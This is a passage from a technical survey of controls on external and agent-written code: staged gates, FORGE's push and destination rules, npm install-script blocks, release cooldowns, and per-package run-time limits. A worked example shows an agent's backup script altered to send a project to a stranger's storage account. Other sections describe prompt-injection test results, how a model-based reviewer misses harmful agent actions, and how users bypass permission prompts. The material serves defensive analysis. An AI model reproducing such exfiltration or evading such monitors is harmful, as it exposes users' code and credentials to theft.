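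*ZitPit* (Taylor, Brousseau and colleagues, 2026) describes an open-source gate that grants access in stages. It holds external code that is new to it and assigns that code one of seven verdicts.

| Verdict | What it permits |
|---|---|
| `FETCH_ONLY` | Downloading the code, but not running it on a protected machine |
| `UNPACK_ONLY` | Unpacking and inspecting it |
| `BUILD_NO_NETWORK` | Building it in a controlled environment without general network access |
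| `TEST_NO_SECRETS` | Testing it in isolation, without sensitive data |
| `RUN_DEV` | Running it on a developer's protected machine |
| `RUN_CI` | Running it in the build system, with stronger proof of identity |
| `BLOCKED` | Nothing |

A package could move up this list as evidence accumulates. The extra requirement for `RUN_CI` makes sense because build systems often hold the credentials for publishing releases. The stages still need separate rules about resources, because `RUN_DEV` doesn't by itself specify which folders the code may read or which hosts it may contact.

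ZitPit saves every decision with the original request, the exact version it resolved to, the provenance result, the context, an expiry date and a link to the evidence. If a package later turns out to be malicious, these records can show where the gate let it run.

Taylor and colleagues argue that developers will bypass a gate that is slower than the public internet, so they timed a small request that asks a Git server for its branches and their current commits. They made the request five times for each of five repositories by each route. Median times were 433 to 1,062 milliseconds directly from the public server, 32 to 44 milliseconds from ZitPit's disk cache, and 13 to 16 milliseconds from its memory cache.

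These results mainly show that a nearby copy is faster than a distant one. The test covered only approved code and did not include full downloads. It also left out the checks on code new to ZitPit, which is where a developer would probably wait longest.

Taylor and colleagues are open about what ZitPit doesn't yet cover:

- npm and PyPI packages, and installers that users download directly
- configuration that takes effect when someone opens a project, such as hooks and agents' memory files
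- some of the code that a Git repository brings in later, including submodules (other repositories nested inside it) and large files stored elsewhere

ZitPit only partly covers Rust build scripts and GitHub Actions. It already handles Git requests, blocks some dangerous commands in supervised sessions, and stops some sensitive uploads. If an agent installed the PDF library from npm, ZitPit could not yet hold it.

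### Why the order of events matters

Some rules depend on what happened earlier. Palumbo and colleagues tested one such rule on a coding agent in VS Code Copilot Chat, where FORGE blocks `git push`, the command that sends code to a shared repository, until a security scan has passed on every recent edit. The rule therefore covers code that the agent wrote. It is written in Datalog, a language for logical rules, and looks roughly like this:

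```
Covered(e)   :- RecentEdit(e), ScanPassed(s), DependsOn(s, e).
Uncovered(e) :- RecentEdit(e), not Covered(e).
Deny(a)      :- IsPush(a), Uncovered(e).
```

The symbol `:-` means "if", and the commas mean "and". An edit is covered if a passing scan depends on it, and FORGE denies a push if any edit is uncovered. To apply the rule, FORGE keeps a graph of the agent's messages, tool calls and results, which links each event to the earlier ones that may have influenced it.

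FORGE blocks a push if the code was edited after the last scan. Under a simpler rule, "a scan must have passed during this session", an agent could scan clean code, add a vulnerability and then push, even though the scan covered only the earlier code. FORGE would also block a push after the sequence edit, scan, edit, because the second edit was not scanned.

In the published example, a developer asks for a search feature in a small web service. The agent's code is open to SQL injection, but the unit tests pass because none of them includes an attack. FORGE blocks the push and tells the agent to run the scanner, which finds the flaw. The agent rewrites the query, the code passes both this scan and a separate one for secrets, and the push goes through. Another rule blocks further edits once the agent has changed more than 1,000 lines without a passing scan, so that scans catch problems earlier.

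The paper demonstrates the rule but doesn't measure how often it would prevent flaws in practice. FORGE also depends on the scanner, which would probably pass the invoice page despite its missing access check. The published rule accepts any scan result that contains the text `PASS`, so a failed report that quoted a variable called `DB_PASSWORD` would seem to satisfy it.

Checking the rules takes little time. In a separate customer-service test, FORGE's median decision took less than a millisecond.

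### A backup script in four versions

Suppose a developer asks an agent for a script that backs up the project folder `/work/shop` to the company's account with a cloud storage service. The important lines of the script are:

```python
data = pack("/work/shop", skip=[".env"])
put("https://storage.example/acme-backups/shop.zip", data, token)
```

The first line packs the folder into one file and leaves out `.env`, where projects often keep passwords. The second uploads the file to the account `acme-backups`. The script needs a credential for this, so a policy can't simply forbid credentials. Written in plain rules, the policy might be:

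1. These rules cover backup scripts that the agent writes for this project, when they run on a developer's laptop. Each verdict applies to one exact file.
2. The script may read `/work/shop`, except `.env`.
3. It may use the backup token that the host program supplies, and no other credential.
4. It may connect to `storage.example` and no other host.
5. It may not start other programs or write outside a temporary folder.
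6. If the script reads `.env` or any other credential, block it. If it breaks another rule, hold it for review.
7. If the trial run fails or records no upload, hold it for review.

The gate runs four versions of the script in a sandbox and records the files they read and the hosts they contact.

| Version | Files read | Hosts contacted | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| Intended script | Project folder | `storage.example` | Allow with limits |
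| Also reads credentials | Project folder, the developer's SSH key | `storage.example` | Block |
| Contacts a new host | Project folder | `storage.example`, `stats.example` | Hold for review |
| Uploads to a stranger's account | Project folder | `storage.example` | Allow with limits |

The limits for the intended script are the same rules, applied while it runs.

A backup doesn't need an SSH key, which can give access to other machines, so the block is reasonable even if the agent included the key by mistake. The new host is harder to judge because it may collect stolen files or only count completed backups, but a reviewer can find out which. A system that counts critical findings, as Preflight does, would probably treat these two versions alike, since each adds one.

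The last version differs from the intended script by a single name:

```python
put("https://storage.example/k7-archive/shop.zip", data, token)
```

The stranger who owns `k7-archive` has set it to accept uploads from any customer of the service, so the company's own token works. The script reads the same files, uses the same credential and contacts the same host. Its host-level fingerprint is identical to that of the intended script, and the gate lets it send the whole project to the stranger. (Some storage services include the account name in the hostname. An exact list of hosts would then catch this version, but a rule that allowed every address at the service would not.)

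### Whether behaviour reveals intent

The example directly tests Ammon's claim that the behaviour of malware "cannot conceal its intent". Chris O'Ferrell, chief executive of CodeHunter, makes a more careful version of the argument in the Help Net Security interview *When security decisions come too late, and attackers know it*. O'Ferrell argues that AI can endlessly rewrite how code looks but can't hide the basic actions the code has to take.

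The stranger's version fits O'Ferrell's wording, because the upload happens and the gate records it, but it contradicts Ammon's wording, because a legitimate backup leaves the same record.

If the record included the account name, the two versions would look different, but the names still wouldn't show which upload was theft. `k7-archive` might belong to a contractor paid to store the company's backups, and a thief could have registered `acme-backups`. Establishing who owns an account and whether the developer agreed to use it requires information from outside the program.

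There may also be no bad intent, since an agent that copied `k7-archive` from an outdated README would produce exactly the same script as an attacker. It is therefore better for a policy to check whether someone has authorised the destination, which can be determined in both cases. This still requires evidence of observed behaviour, but that evidence has to include the destination, and someone has to supply a list of authorised destinations to compare it with.

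### Finer rules and what they cost

A rule allowing the script to upload only to `acme-backups` would catch the last version. But a filter that checks only hostnames can't enforce it, because the account name is in the encrypted part of the web request.

The built-in network filter in Claude Code's sandbox filters traffic by hostname. Anthropic warns that allowing a broad domain such as `github.com` can open a path for stealing data, and Docker gives the same warning about its own sandbox. For users who need more protection, Anthropic suggests a custom proxy that decrypts and inspects traffic. The sandbox then has to trust the proxy's certificate, and programs that accept only certain certificates may stop working. The proxy can also read everything that passes through it, including passwords, which makes it an attractive target.

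Some cloud services can enforce the rule themselves. AWS's *Preventing data exfiltration in a private VPC* covers a nearly identical case, in which users copy data from a company's storage into their own accounts on the same service. The company sends its storage traffic through a controlled exit from its private network, where a policy accepts a request only if it concerns a named storage container and comes from a listed account. This would stop the script whether it used the company's token or the stranger's.

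AWS notes that its sample policy still permits some administrative operations that could send file names to outside accounts. Closing that gap requires additional rules. The protection also applies only to traffic that uses the controlled exit, so a script on a laptop at home could avoid it. Someone also has to keep the lists current. AWS's *Establish permissions guardrails using data perimeters* cautions that broad boundaries like these don't remove the need to keep adjusting individual permissions.

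A third approach keeps the real credential away from the code. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes how Claude Code on the web does this for Git. The code in the sandbox gets a limited credential that works only with a proxy. According to Anthropic, the proxy checks what the request would do, including the branch name and destination repository, before adding the real credential. A similar proxy for backups could check the account name, but someone would have to write and maintain a proxy for each service.

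FORGE can trace where a destination came from. One of its policies lets an agent that has read untrusted text send data only to destinations in the user's request or on a trusted list. If the agent uploaded the data through a tool with a destination field, this policy would reject `k7-archive` unless the developer had named it. If the agent ran `python backup.py` instead, the name would be inside the script, and FORGE would need a way to extract it.

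Palumbo and colleagues measured the drawbacks of this kind of precision using AgentDojo's prompt-injection tests, which include no coding. Their agent was based on GPT-4o, now an old model. In all three of these configurations, the agent also saw the user's request again after each batch of tool results.

| Added policy | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.1% | 83.7% |
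| Block all consequential actions after the agent reads untrusted text | 0.6% | 33.2% |
| Check what the user requested and where each destination came from | 0.9% | 62.5% |

The finer policy was nearly as secure as the coarser one and let the agent complete almost twice as many tasks. Its completion rate was still about 21 percentage points lower than with no policy. In the 151 attack-free runs where FORGE refused an action, the agent recovered and completed the task in only 36.

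### The record of earlier permission systems

Jeff Williams, chief technology officer and co-founder of the application security company Contrast Security, considers zero trust for code a sound principle with a mixed record. The examples Williams gave ReversingLabs include the Java sandbox, which restricted what Java programs could do, and SELinux, which adds mandatory access rules to Linux. Williams said such systems struggled because their policies were cumbersome, hard to maintain and prone to breaking legitimate software. Developers often need to open network connections or start other programs, and when a control interferes, people usually weaken it or turn it off.

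Data from Claude Code fits this account well. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets certain shell commands run without approval. Many of these rules are very broad. One common type allows any command starting with `python`, which in practice lets the agent do almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks bypassed altogether. Anthropic published these figures to promote an alternative to permission prompts, but they are direct evidence of what its users do.

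Williams names mobile phones as the exception. Apple and Google can make permissions mandatory because they control the operating systems, app stores and app distribution. Williams sees no comparable leverage over software in general. A company has some leverage over its own coding agents. Garner Health, for example, used central settings to make Anthropic's new mode the default for all 550 employees. A company can also decide what runs on its build servers. But it doesn't control the outside developers whose packages it uses, and a rule that breaks their software will probably still prompt requests for exceptions.

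Williams's last objection is specific to agents. An agent may legitimately need to read data, write code, send messages and run commands across many systems. Williams argues that when an agent's possible behaviour is "almost everything", nobody can write down in advance all that it should and shouldn't do.

The objection is strong against a single policy for the whole agent. It is weaker against policies for the individual things an agent produces, because the backup script needs only one folder, one token and one account, even if the agent that wrote it can do far more. The FORGE push rule avoids the problem by setting a condition for one important action and leaving most of the agent's other work alone. But someone has to write a policy for each new kind of script, and a rule about pushes doesn't protect against a harmful upload.

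Language models could write many of these small policies, but the evidence so far suggests that people would need to check them. Palumbo and colleagues had a model translate an airline's customer-service rules into Datalog five times and tested each translation on three tasks, with five attempts per task. Two translations passed every trial, as did the policy written by hand. The worst translation failed one task in all five attempts.

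Most of the failures came from translations that blocked legitimate cancellations. One cause was that the faulty translations required a particular kind of reason for every cancellation, while the airline's rules require it only if the customer is relying on travel insurance. All five translations had matched a judge model's decision in every case recorded during development, so testing a policy against past cases may not reveal that it is too strict.

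### Approval prompts

A gate can leave the hard cases to a person, but this works only if the person reads them. Brian Jack, chief information security officer at the security training company KnowBe4, told ReversingLabs that asking users for approval is an old idea and can be a very good control when done well. If users get too many prompts, they approve them by default. Jack also doubts that all users know equally well what a piece of software should be doing.

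Anthropic reports that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. That figure alone is weak evidence that users approve carelessly, since most of the commands are probably safe. A controlled study gives better evidence. Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers, who believed they were taking part in a coding study, and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

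The testers worked in an unfamiliar test environment with nothing of their own at risk, so they may have been less careful than they would be at work. Because each tester saw only one dangerous command, the early and late figures compare different people. Even so, the results support Jack's warning. If a gate relies on frequent approvals, most of its reviewers can be expected to miss a dangerous command.

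Asking users less often, and about larger decisions, may help. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. Some of the plan rejections presumably concern quality rather than safety. For the backup script, one question about which account should receive the files would probably be more useful than a separate prompt for each command.

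Anthropic's alternative is auto mode, in which a language model reviews the agent's riskier actions. It blocked 89% of the dangerous commands in the study, but Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that an earlier version missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what the user wanted. That version also wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewing model identified the danger but was wrong about whether the user had consented to it. A request to "clean up the PR", for example, doesn't authorise the agent to overwrite the project's history. The model receives the user's messages and the agent's commands but not the results of those commands, which protects it from instructions planted in files. If the backup script took its account name from an existing settings file, the model might never receive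 the name `k7-archive`.

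## Making the verdict hold when the code runs

Suppose the gate has allowed the backup script, which reads the name of the storage account from `settings.json`. A week later, someone changes the name in that file from `acme-backups` to `k7-archive`. The script hasn't changed since the gate examined it, but it now sends the project to a stranger's storage account.

A verdict can also fail because some code never goes through the gate, or because a dependency does something at run time that no earlier check revealed.

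### Tying a verdict to the files

A gate can store an artifact's cryptographic hash with the verdict and recompute the hash just before the run, so the verdict doesn't carry over to a changed file. The program then has to run from the copy the gate hashed, because someone could otherwise change the file between the check and the start.

A lockfile lists the exact version of every package a project uses, including indirect dependencies, and usually a hash of each. A verdict that includes the lockfile's hash therefore applies only to that set of packages. Preflight's certificate works roughly this way.

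Neither hash would reveal the change to `settings.json`. Hossen (2026), in *When the Approved File Is Unchanged*, measured how often this kind of change happens. The study covers projects' own files, such as deployment instructions, not packages or agent-written code. In a typical case, a reviewer approves a workflow file that does little more than run Terraform, a tool that creates cloud resources. The permissions that the deployment grants are in other files.

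Hossen searched GitHub for files that rely on other files to do part of their work, and followed the references by hand to find every file that determines the outcome. The search yielded 20 public repositories, each with a set of 2 to 44 such files. Hossen then examined up to 500 commits in each repository, 5,251 in total. At least one file in the set changed in 542 of them. In 296 of those 542 (54.6%), the approved file stayed the same, so checking only that file would have missed the change.

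Most of these ordinary edits were presumably harmless. The percentage comes from projects that Hossen chose because their approved file depends on others, so it isn't a rate for approvals in general. One repository accounts for 130 of the 296 commits, and without it the share falls to 43.6%. But the problem occurred in 15 of the 20 repositories, and Hossen showed on local copies that such an edit can matter. In one project, changing a single line in a settings file lowered the number of human approvals required for high-risk changes from one to zero, even though the approved file, which contains the rules for those decisions, was unchanged.

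The simplest remedy is to approve a whole commit and run exactly that commit. This doesn't suit a standing approval, such as permission for an agent to run a deployment command for the next month, because any later commit would end it. For these cases, Hossen proposes a combined hash of all the files that the run is configured to read:

D = H(name₁, H(file₁), name₂, H(file₂), …)

Here H is the hash function, and the file names are in a fixed order. Hossen calls such an approval sound if it covers every file the run is configured to read, and exact if it covers those files and no others. In the 20 repositories, this method would have required a new approval on about one commit in ten.

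Listing the files is the difficult part. Hossen asked two coding agents, Codex CLI and Claude Code, to choose the files and compute the combined hash for four tasks. They computed the hash correctly in 61 of 62 runs and covered all the necessary files in 59. But in 16 runs on the same Terraform deployment, they chose five different sets of files, and in two of those runs they included none of the 42 Terraform files. Nobody can tell from the hash alone whether the agent chose the right files. The agents used models from before June 2026, and newer ones may be more consistent.

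Hossen concludes that the gate should compute the hash itself and treat the agent's list only as a proposal. More reliable alternatives to that list can be the deployment tool's record of what it reads, a list that people have reviewed, or a rule that covers whole directories. A directory rule is easy to write but requires some unnecessary approvals, and in two of the three tasks that involved several files, one necessary file was outside the main directories. The hash covers only files in the repository, so if the backup script read its account name from an environment variable, the gate would have to check that variable separately.

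### Routes that miss the gate

A gate on the connection to a package registry doesn't examine code that arrives or starts in other ways:

- packages that come from a Git repository or a web address instead of the registry
- programs, scripts and editor extensions that someone downloads directly
- other people's source code that an agent copies into the project
- hooks, editor tasks and build files that run commands when someone opens, builds or tests the project
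- scripts and tools that an agent's own configuration starts
- code that an approved program downloads or generates as it runs

ZitPit's developers list several of these among its gaps. A company can limit the first two routes by letting the agent's machine reach the internet only through the gate, but this doesn't address files already in the repository.

Agent configuration is a fairly new route. An agent can load "skills", which are task instructions that may include scripts, and hooks, which run commands at set points in its work. It can also start tool servers, programs that give it extra abilities, such as searching a database, and usually follow a standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). A repository can contain settings for all of these, and for which commands the agent may run without asking.

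*Scanning the Harness* (Kapner, Soceanu and colleagues, 2026) examined such settings in 3,171 public GitHub repositories. Of those, 2,660 were "setups" that combined at least two kinds of component, and the rest were collections of skills. A scanner looked for risky settings, a second program repeated its checks, and a language model and one of the researchers reviewed the results. The study found at least one of three problems in 409 setups (15.4%).

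| Problem | Setups |
|---|---|
| Tool server package with no fixed version | 260 (9.8%) |
| Skill with broad advance approval to use tools | 101 (3.8%) |
| Settings with broad advance approval to run commands | 67 (2.5%) |

(Some setups have more than one problem.)

Without a fixed version, the agent may download and run a different release of the tool server than the one someone examined. Among the 1,063 setups that configured tool servers, 24.5% had this problem. A broad approval might allow any Python program to run, much like the rules many Claude Code users have written themselves. The effect may be more limited for skills, because in Claude Code a skill's advance approval ends with the user's next message, and rules that forbid a command still apply.

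Kapner and colleagues measured what the files contain, not what happened when agents used them. Some of the broad approvals may be deliberate, and a sandbox could limit the damage. The search favoured projects that advertise their agent tooling, so the figures don't describe all repositories. Such scans are also hard to get right. Both programs initially treated broad approvals of the search command `find` as dangerous, because `find` can start other programs. The researchers removed 62 findings because, according to Claude Code's documentation, such approvals don't cover that use.

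Turning a feature off by default doesn't necessarily stop attackers from using it. The code editor VS Code used to run certain tasks automatically when someone opened a project, and Microsoft turned this off by default in January 2026 after months of attacks. OpenSourceMalware's *npm v12* reports that attackers have continued to use these tasks.

### Blocking install scripts

Package managers have recently begun to block two routes for unapproved code by default. Version 12 of npm, released in July 2026, no longer runs dependencies' install scripts unless the project has approved them, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026). It also refuses dependencies from Git repositories and web addresses unless the user allows them. A Git dependency could previously run code during installation even when scripts were off, according to GitHub's *Upcoming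 breaking changes for npm v12* (2026). The block on install scripts also covers packages that have no install script but that npm would compile automatically.

This default would probably have stopped the Axios malware, which relied on an install script.

A user can list the blocked scripts and approve the ones the project needs. npm saves the approvals in `package.json`, so everyone who works on the project shares them. An agent that can edit this file can approve scripts too, unless the host program prevents it. OpenSourceMalware expects people to approve scripts out of habit, as they do with browser prompts, and Anthropic's study of permission prompts supports this concern.

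An approval may also carry over to code that was never checked. In pnpm, another package manager for JavaScript, a project can approve a package by name, which presumably covers later versions. pnpm's *Mitigating supply chain attacks* advises caution when updating a trusted package that has an install script, because an attacker may have compromised the package since it was last installed. A gate could avoid this by approving the script's hash instead of the package's name.

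Blocking covers only dependencies' scripts, so the project's own scripts still run.

### Waiting periods for new releases

A cooldown keeps a project from installing a release until it has been public for a set time, which gives other people a chance to find malware first. *Package managers need to cool down* (2026) cites William Woodruff's review of ten supply-chain attacks, eight of which had a window of opportunity of less than a week. A seven-day wait would have kept most of these attacks from reaching users. A one-day wait would have blocked the malicious versions of Axios, which stayed up for about three hours.

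The main JavaScript package managers now have these defaults:

| Package manager | Dependencies' install scripts | Waiting period |
|---|---|---|
| npm 12 | Blocked unless approved | Off unless the user sets one |
| pnpm 11 | Blocked unless approved | One day, with automatic exceptions |
| Yarn 4 (recent versions) | Blocked unless approved | One day |
| Bun | Blocked, except for a built-in list of popular packages | Available as a setting |

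Mansharof (2026) reports the waiting periods for pnpm and Yarn in *Recently published NPM packages may be blocked for 24 hours*. According to blog.stephane-robert.info, npm's waiting period was still off by default after version 12 came out. Yarn began blocking scripts in April 2026. According to Bun's *Add a trusted dependency*, Bun's built-in list applies only to packages from npm, and a project can replace it with its own.

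pnpm's one-day wait is weaker than it sounds. Kochan, in *pnpm 11.0*, lists strict enforcement as off by default. According to the release notes in *npm pnpm 11.1.3*, if pnpm selects a release that is too new, it adds the release to the project's list of exceptions and continues with the installation. An agent that asks for an hour-old package could therefore still get it. A team that wants the delay to hold has to turn on the strict setting.

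Outside JavaScript, waiting periods are mostly optional or unfinished. The Python installers pip, uv and Poetry offer one, as does Bundler for Ruby. Cargo, for Rust, has an experimental version. Go has only a proposal, and *Package managers need to cool down* found no discussion of the idea for Maven.

Some projects get the delay from a tool that proposes updates. According to GitHub, Dependabot has waited three days by default since July 2026 before proposing an ordinary update, but it proposes security fixes immediately. Delaying those fixes would leave known flaws open for longer. Dependabot's delay doesn't apply when a developer or an agent installs a package directly.

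Malware could still be caught if everyone waited before installing new packages, because much of the detection comes from researchers and scanners that examine packages as soon as they appear, as happened with TanStack. Waiting helps less against malware that they miss, and it may do nothing against a package registered under a name that a model invented, because that package could be months old by the time an agent installs it.

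### How ZTD-Java limits a dependency

Harmful code may still get through these checks, so a last control limits what each dependency can do while the program runs. An ordinary sandbox limits the program as a whole, so the PDF library gets whatever access the invoice page needs. Limiting the library alone requires a way to tell which package each request comes from.

Amusuo, Robinson and colleagues (2023), in *ZTD_JAVA*, apply NIST's zero-trust architecture to the packages inside a Java program. Their system, ZTD-Java, first learns what each package needs and then denies everything else:

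1. The developer runs the program on typical tasks, such as its existing tests.
2. ZTD-Java records every file that a package reads or writes, every connection it opens and every command it runs.
3. It turns the record into a policy for each package, which the developer can review and edit.
4. When the program runs for real, ZTD-Java checks each new request against these policies.

To intercept the requests, ZTD-Java inserts a check into four functions of Java's standard library as the program loads them. One opens files for reading, one opens files for writing, one makes network connections and one starts other programs. The check looks at the call stack, the chain of functions that are waiting for the current one to finish, and works out from their names which packages they belong to. It allows access to a resource r only if

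r ∈ P(d) for every dependency d on the call stack

where P(d) is the set of resources that d may use, directly or through another package. Suppose a small date library has never used the network in the test runs. It can't open a connection itself, and it can't get a web library to open one for it, because the date library would still be on the stack.

The policy can be coarse, such as "may read files", or it can name particular files, hosts and commands. Developers can choose whether a violation stops the request or only sends an alert.

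Amusuo and colleagues examined how much detail such policies need. In a random sample of 118 serious vulnerabilities in popular Java libraries, 55 could give an attacker access to files, the network or a shell. In 32 of the 55, the library didn't need that kind of access, so a coarse rule denying it entirely would be enough. The other 23 (42%) would need a rule about particular files, hosts or commands. Shell access was the easiest to deny, because the library never needed it in 27 of the 36 cases that exposed it.

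Policies based on observed runs can also be much shorter than lists based on code analysis. Among 103 dependencies of nine programs, 46 contained code that could read files, but only four read any during the test runs. Fifteen could run shell commands, but none did.

### How NodeShield limits a dependency

Cornelissen and Balliu built NodeShield for Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside the browser. Its permissions are broader and fall into seven categories: files, network, commands, system information, cryptography, running generated code, and loading native code (compiled code that runs outside JavaScript's control). NodeShield uses the program's SBOM to determine which other packages each package may load, and a capability list to determine which of the seven categories each package may use.

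If there is no capability list yet, NodeShield makes one by searching the source code for the names of sensitive functions and modules. Developers can also run the program in a mode that only logs violations, then add any missing capabilities to the list. This makes the list more accurate, but any malware in the program would run without restrictions during that run.

NodeShield then makes a copy of the project in which each source file runs in its own JavaScript environment. It controls access there in three places:

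- when a package loads another package or one of Node.js's own modules
- when it uses a global function, such as `fetch` for web requests
- when it tries to reach the native code underneath Node.js directly

If the PDF library has permission only for files, it can't load the network module, no matter how it assembles the module's name. Depending on the settings, NodeShield logs the violation, reports an error to the program, or stops the program.

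### What they stopped and what they cost

| | ZTD-Java | NodeShield |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks stopped | Exploits of all 15 vulnerabilities | 66 of 67 malware samples |
| Programs broken | None in the test runs | 3 of 86 |
| Extra running time | At most 2.9% in 16 programs | Less than 1 ms per web request |
| Extra memory | Not reported | 43% to 251% in six servers |

ZTD-Java's tests used 15 accidental flaws in legitimate libraries, including Log4Shell, rather than deliberately malicious code. Amusuo and colleagues first tested all 15 in small sample programs. They then added nine of the vulnerable libraries to real programs and generated policies from those programs' ordinary workloads. The policies blocked every exploit.

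The fact that no programs broke is weaker evidence. The researchers ran the programs on the same workloads that had produced the policies, so nearly everything the programs did was already allowed. A feature those workloads never used, such as a yearly export, could fail the first time someone needed it.

NodeShield's result of 66 out of 67 depends partly on the developer. In most of the samples, the package was malicious from the start. NodeShield's search may find that such a package uses the network and add the network to its list of permissions. The attack then fails only if a developer reviews the list and removes that permission. Malicious updates are a fairer test of automatic protection, because the list can come from the earlier, harmless version. Only four of the packages were updates with malware that acts at run time, and NodeShield stopped three. The researchers had also collected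 almost 1,600 packages that attack through install scripts. They tested five of these and recommend other tools for such attacks.

Three programs were incompatible with NodeShield, mostly because of how they test whether a value is a list. In a separate test of 24 harmless programs, NodeShield raised 18 false alarms and correctly allowed 387 other uses, a false-alarm rate of 4.4% (the paper gives 4.65%). The tests ran only about 15% of the programs' code on average, so longer use would probably reveal more problems.

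NodeShield mainly slows startup and increases memory use. Short command-line programs took between 32% and 434% longer to finish. This would affect an agent that runs many short commands much more than it would affect a web server.

### Behaviour that earlier checks missed

Run-time limits are most useful against behaviour that earlier checks missed. In 2018, an attacker added a dependency called `flatmap-stream` to the `event-stream` package. Its disguised code was designed to act only inside Copay, a cryptocurrency wallet, so a trial run in any other program would probably have shown nothing unusual.

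When Cornelissen and Balliu recreated the attack, the disguise also hid most of it from NodeShield's search of the source code, which found only that `flatmap-stream` used system information. But when the package ran, it also tried to use cryptography, files and the network. The disguise had kept these off the package's list of permissions, so NodeShield blocked the attack. Without the disguise, they would have been on the list, and a developer might have wondered why an update to `event-stream` needed the network.

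The same limits also contain the damage from accidental flaws. NodeShield stopped 21 of 24 exploits that trick a package into running an attacker's code. In the other three, the attacker's code used only access that the package already had.

### When a dependency needs the access it abuses

NodeShield missed one sample, a malicious update to `node-ipc`. The attack needed only file and network access, which the previous, harmless version already used. ZTD-Java's more detailed rules might help in a similar case if the attack used files or hosts that the package had never used before. Such rules work less well for a library like Axios, which contacts whatever address the program gives it.

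A permission to run commands is even harder to contain. NodeShield doesn't control the programs that a package starts or the native code that it loads, so permission to do either can give the package access to everything else. ZTD-Java can restrict which commands a package runs, but native code can bypass its checks. ZTD-Java also can't identify which package made a request if that package passes the work to an independent thread that another package created. An operating-system sandbox around the whole program would limit the damage in these cases, though it couldn't distinguish between packages.

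The two systems also check permissions differently when one package acts through another. ZTD-Java requires permission from every package on the call stack. NodeShield checks only the package that makes the request, so a date library could use the network through a web library that it is allowed to load. Cornelissen and Balliu handle this during review by showing the developer a package's permissions together with those of everything it depends on.

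Neither system checks what a program does with its own data. Of the 118 vulnerabilities in the Java study, 21 were access-control flaws like the one in the invoice page, and Amusuo and colleagues say ZTD-Java is not meant to prevent unauthorised use of an application. ZTD-Java would also miss the change to `settings.json` if the backup script were written in Java, because it checks connections when they open, and the script connects to `storage.example` whichever account will receive the files.
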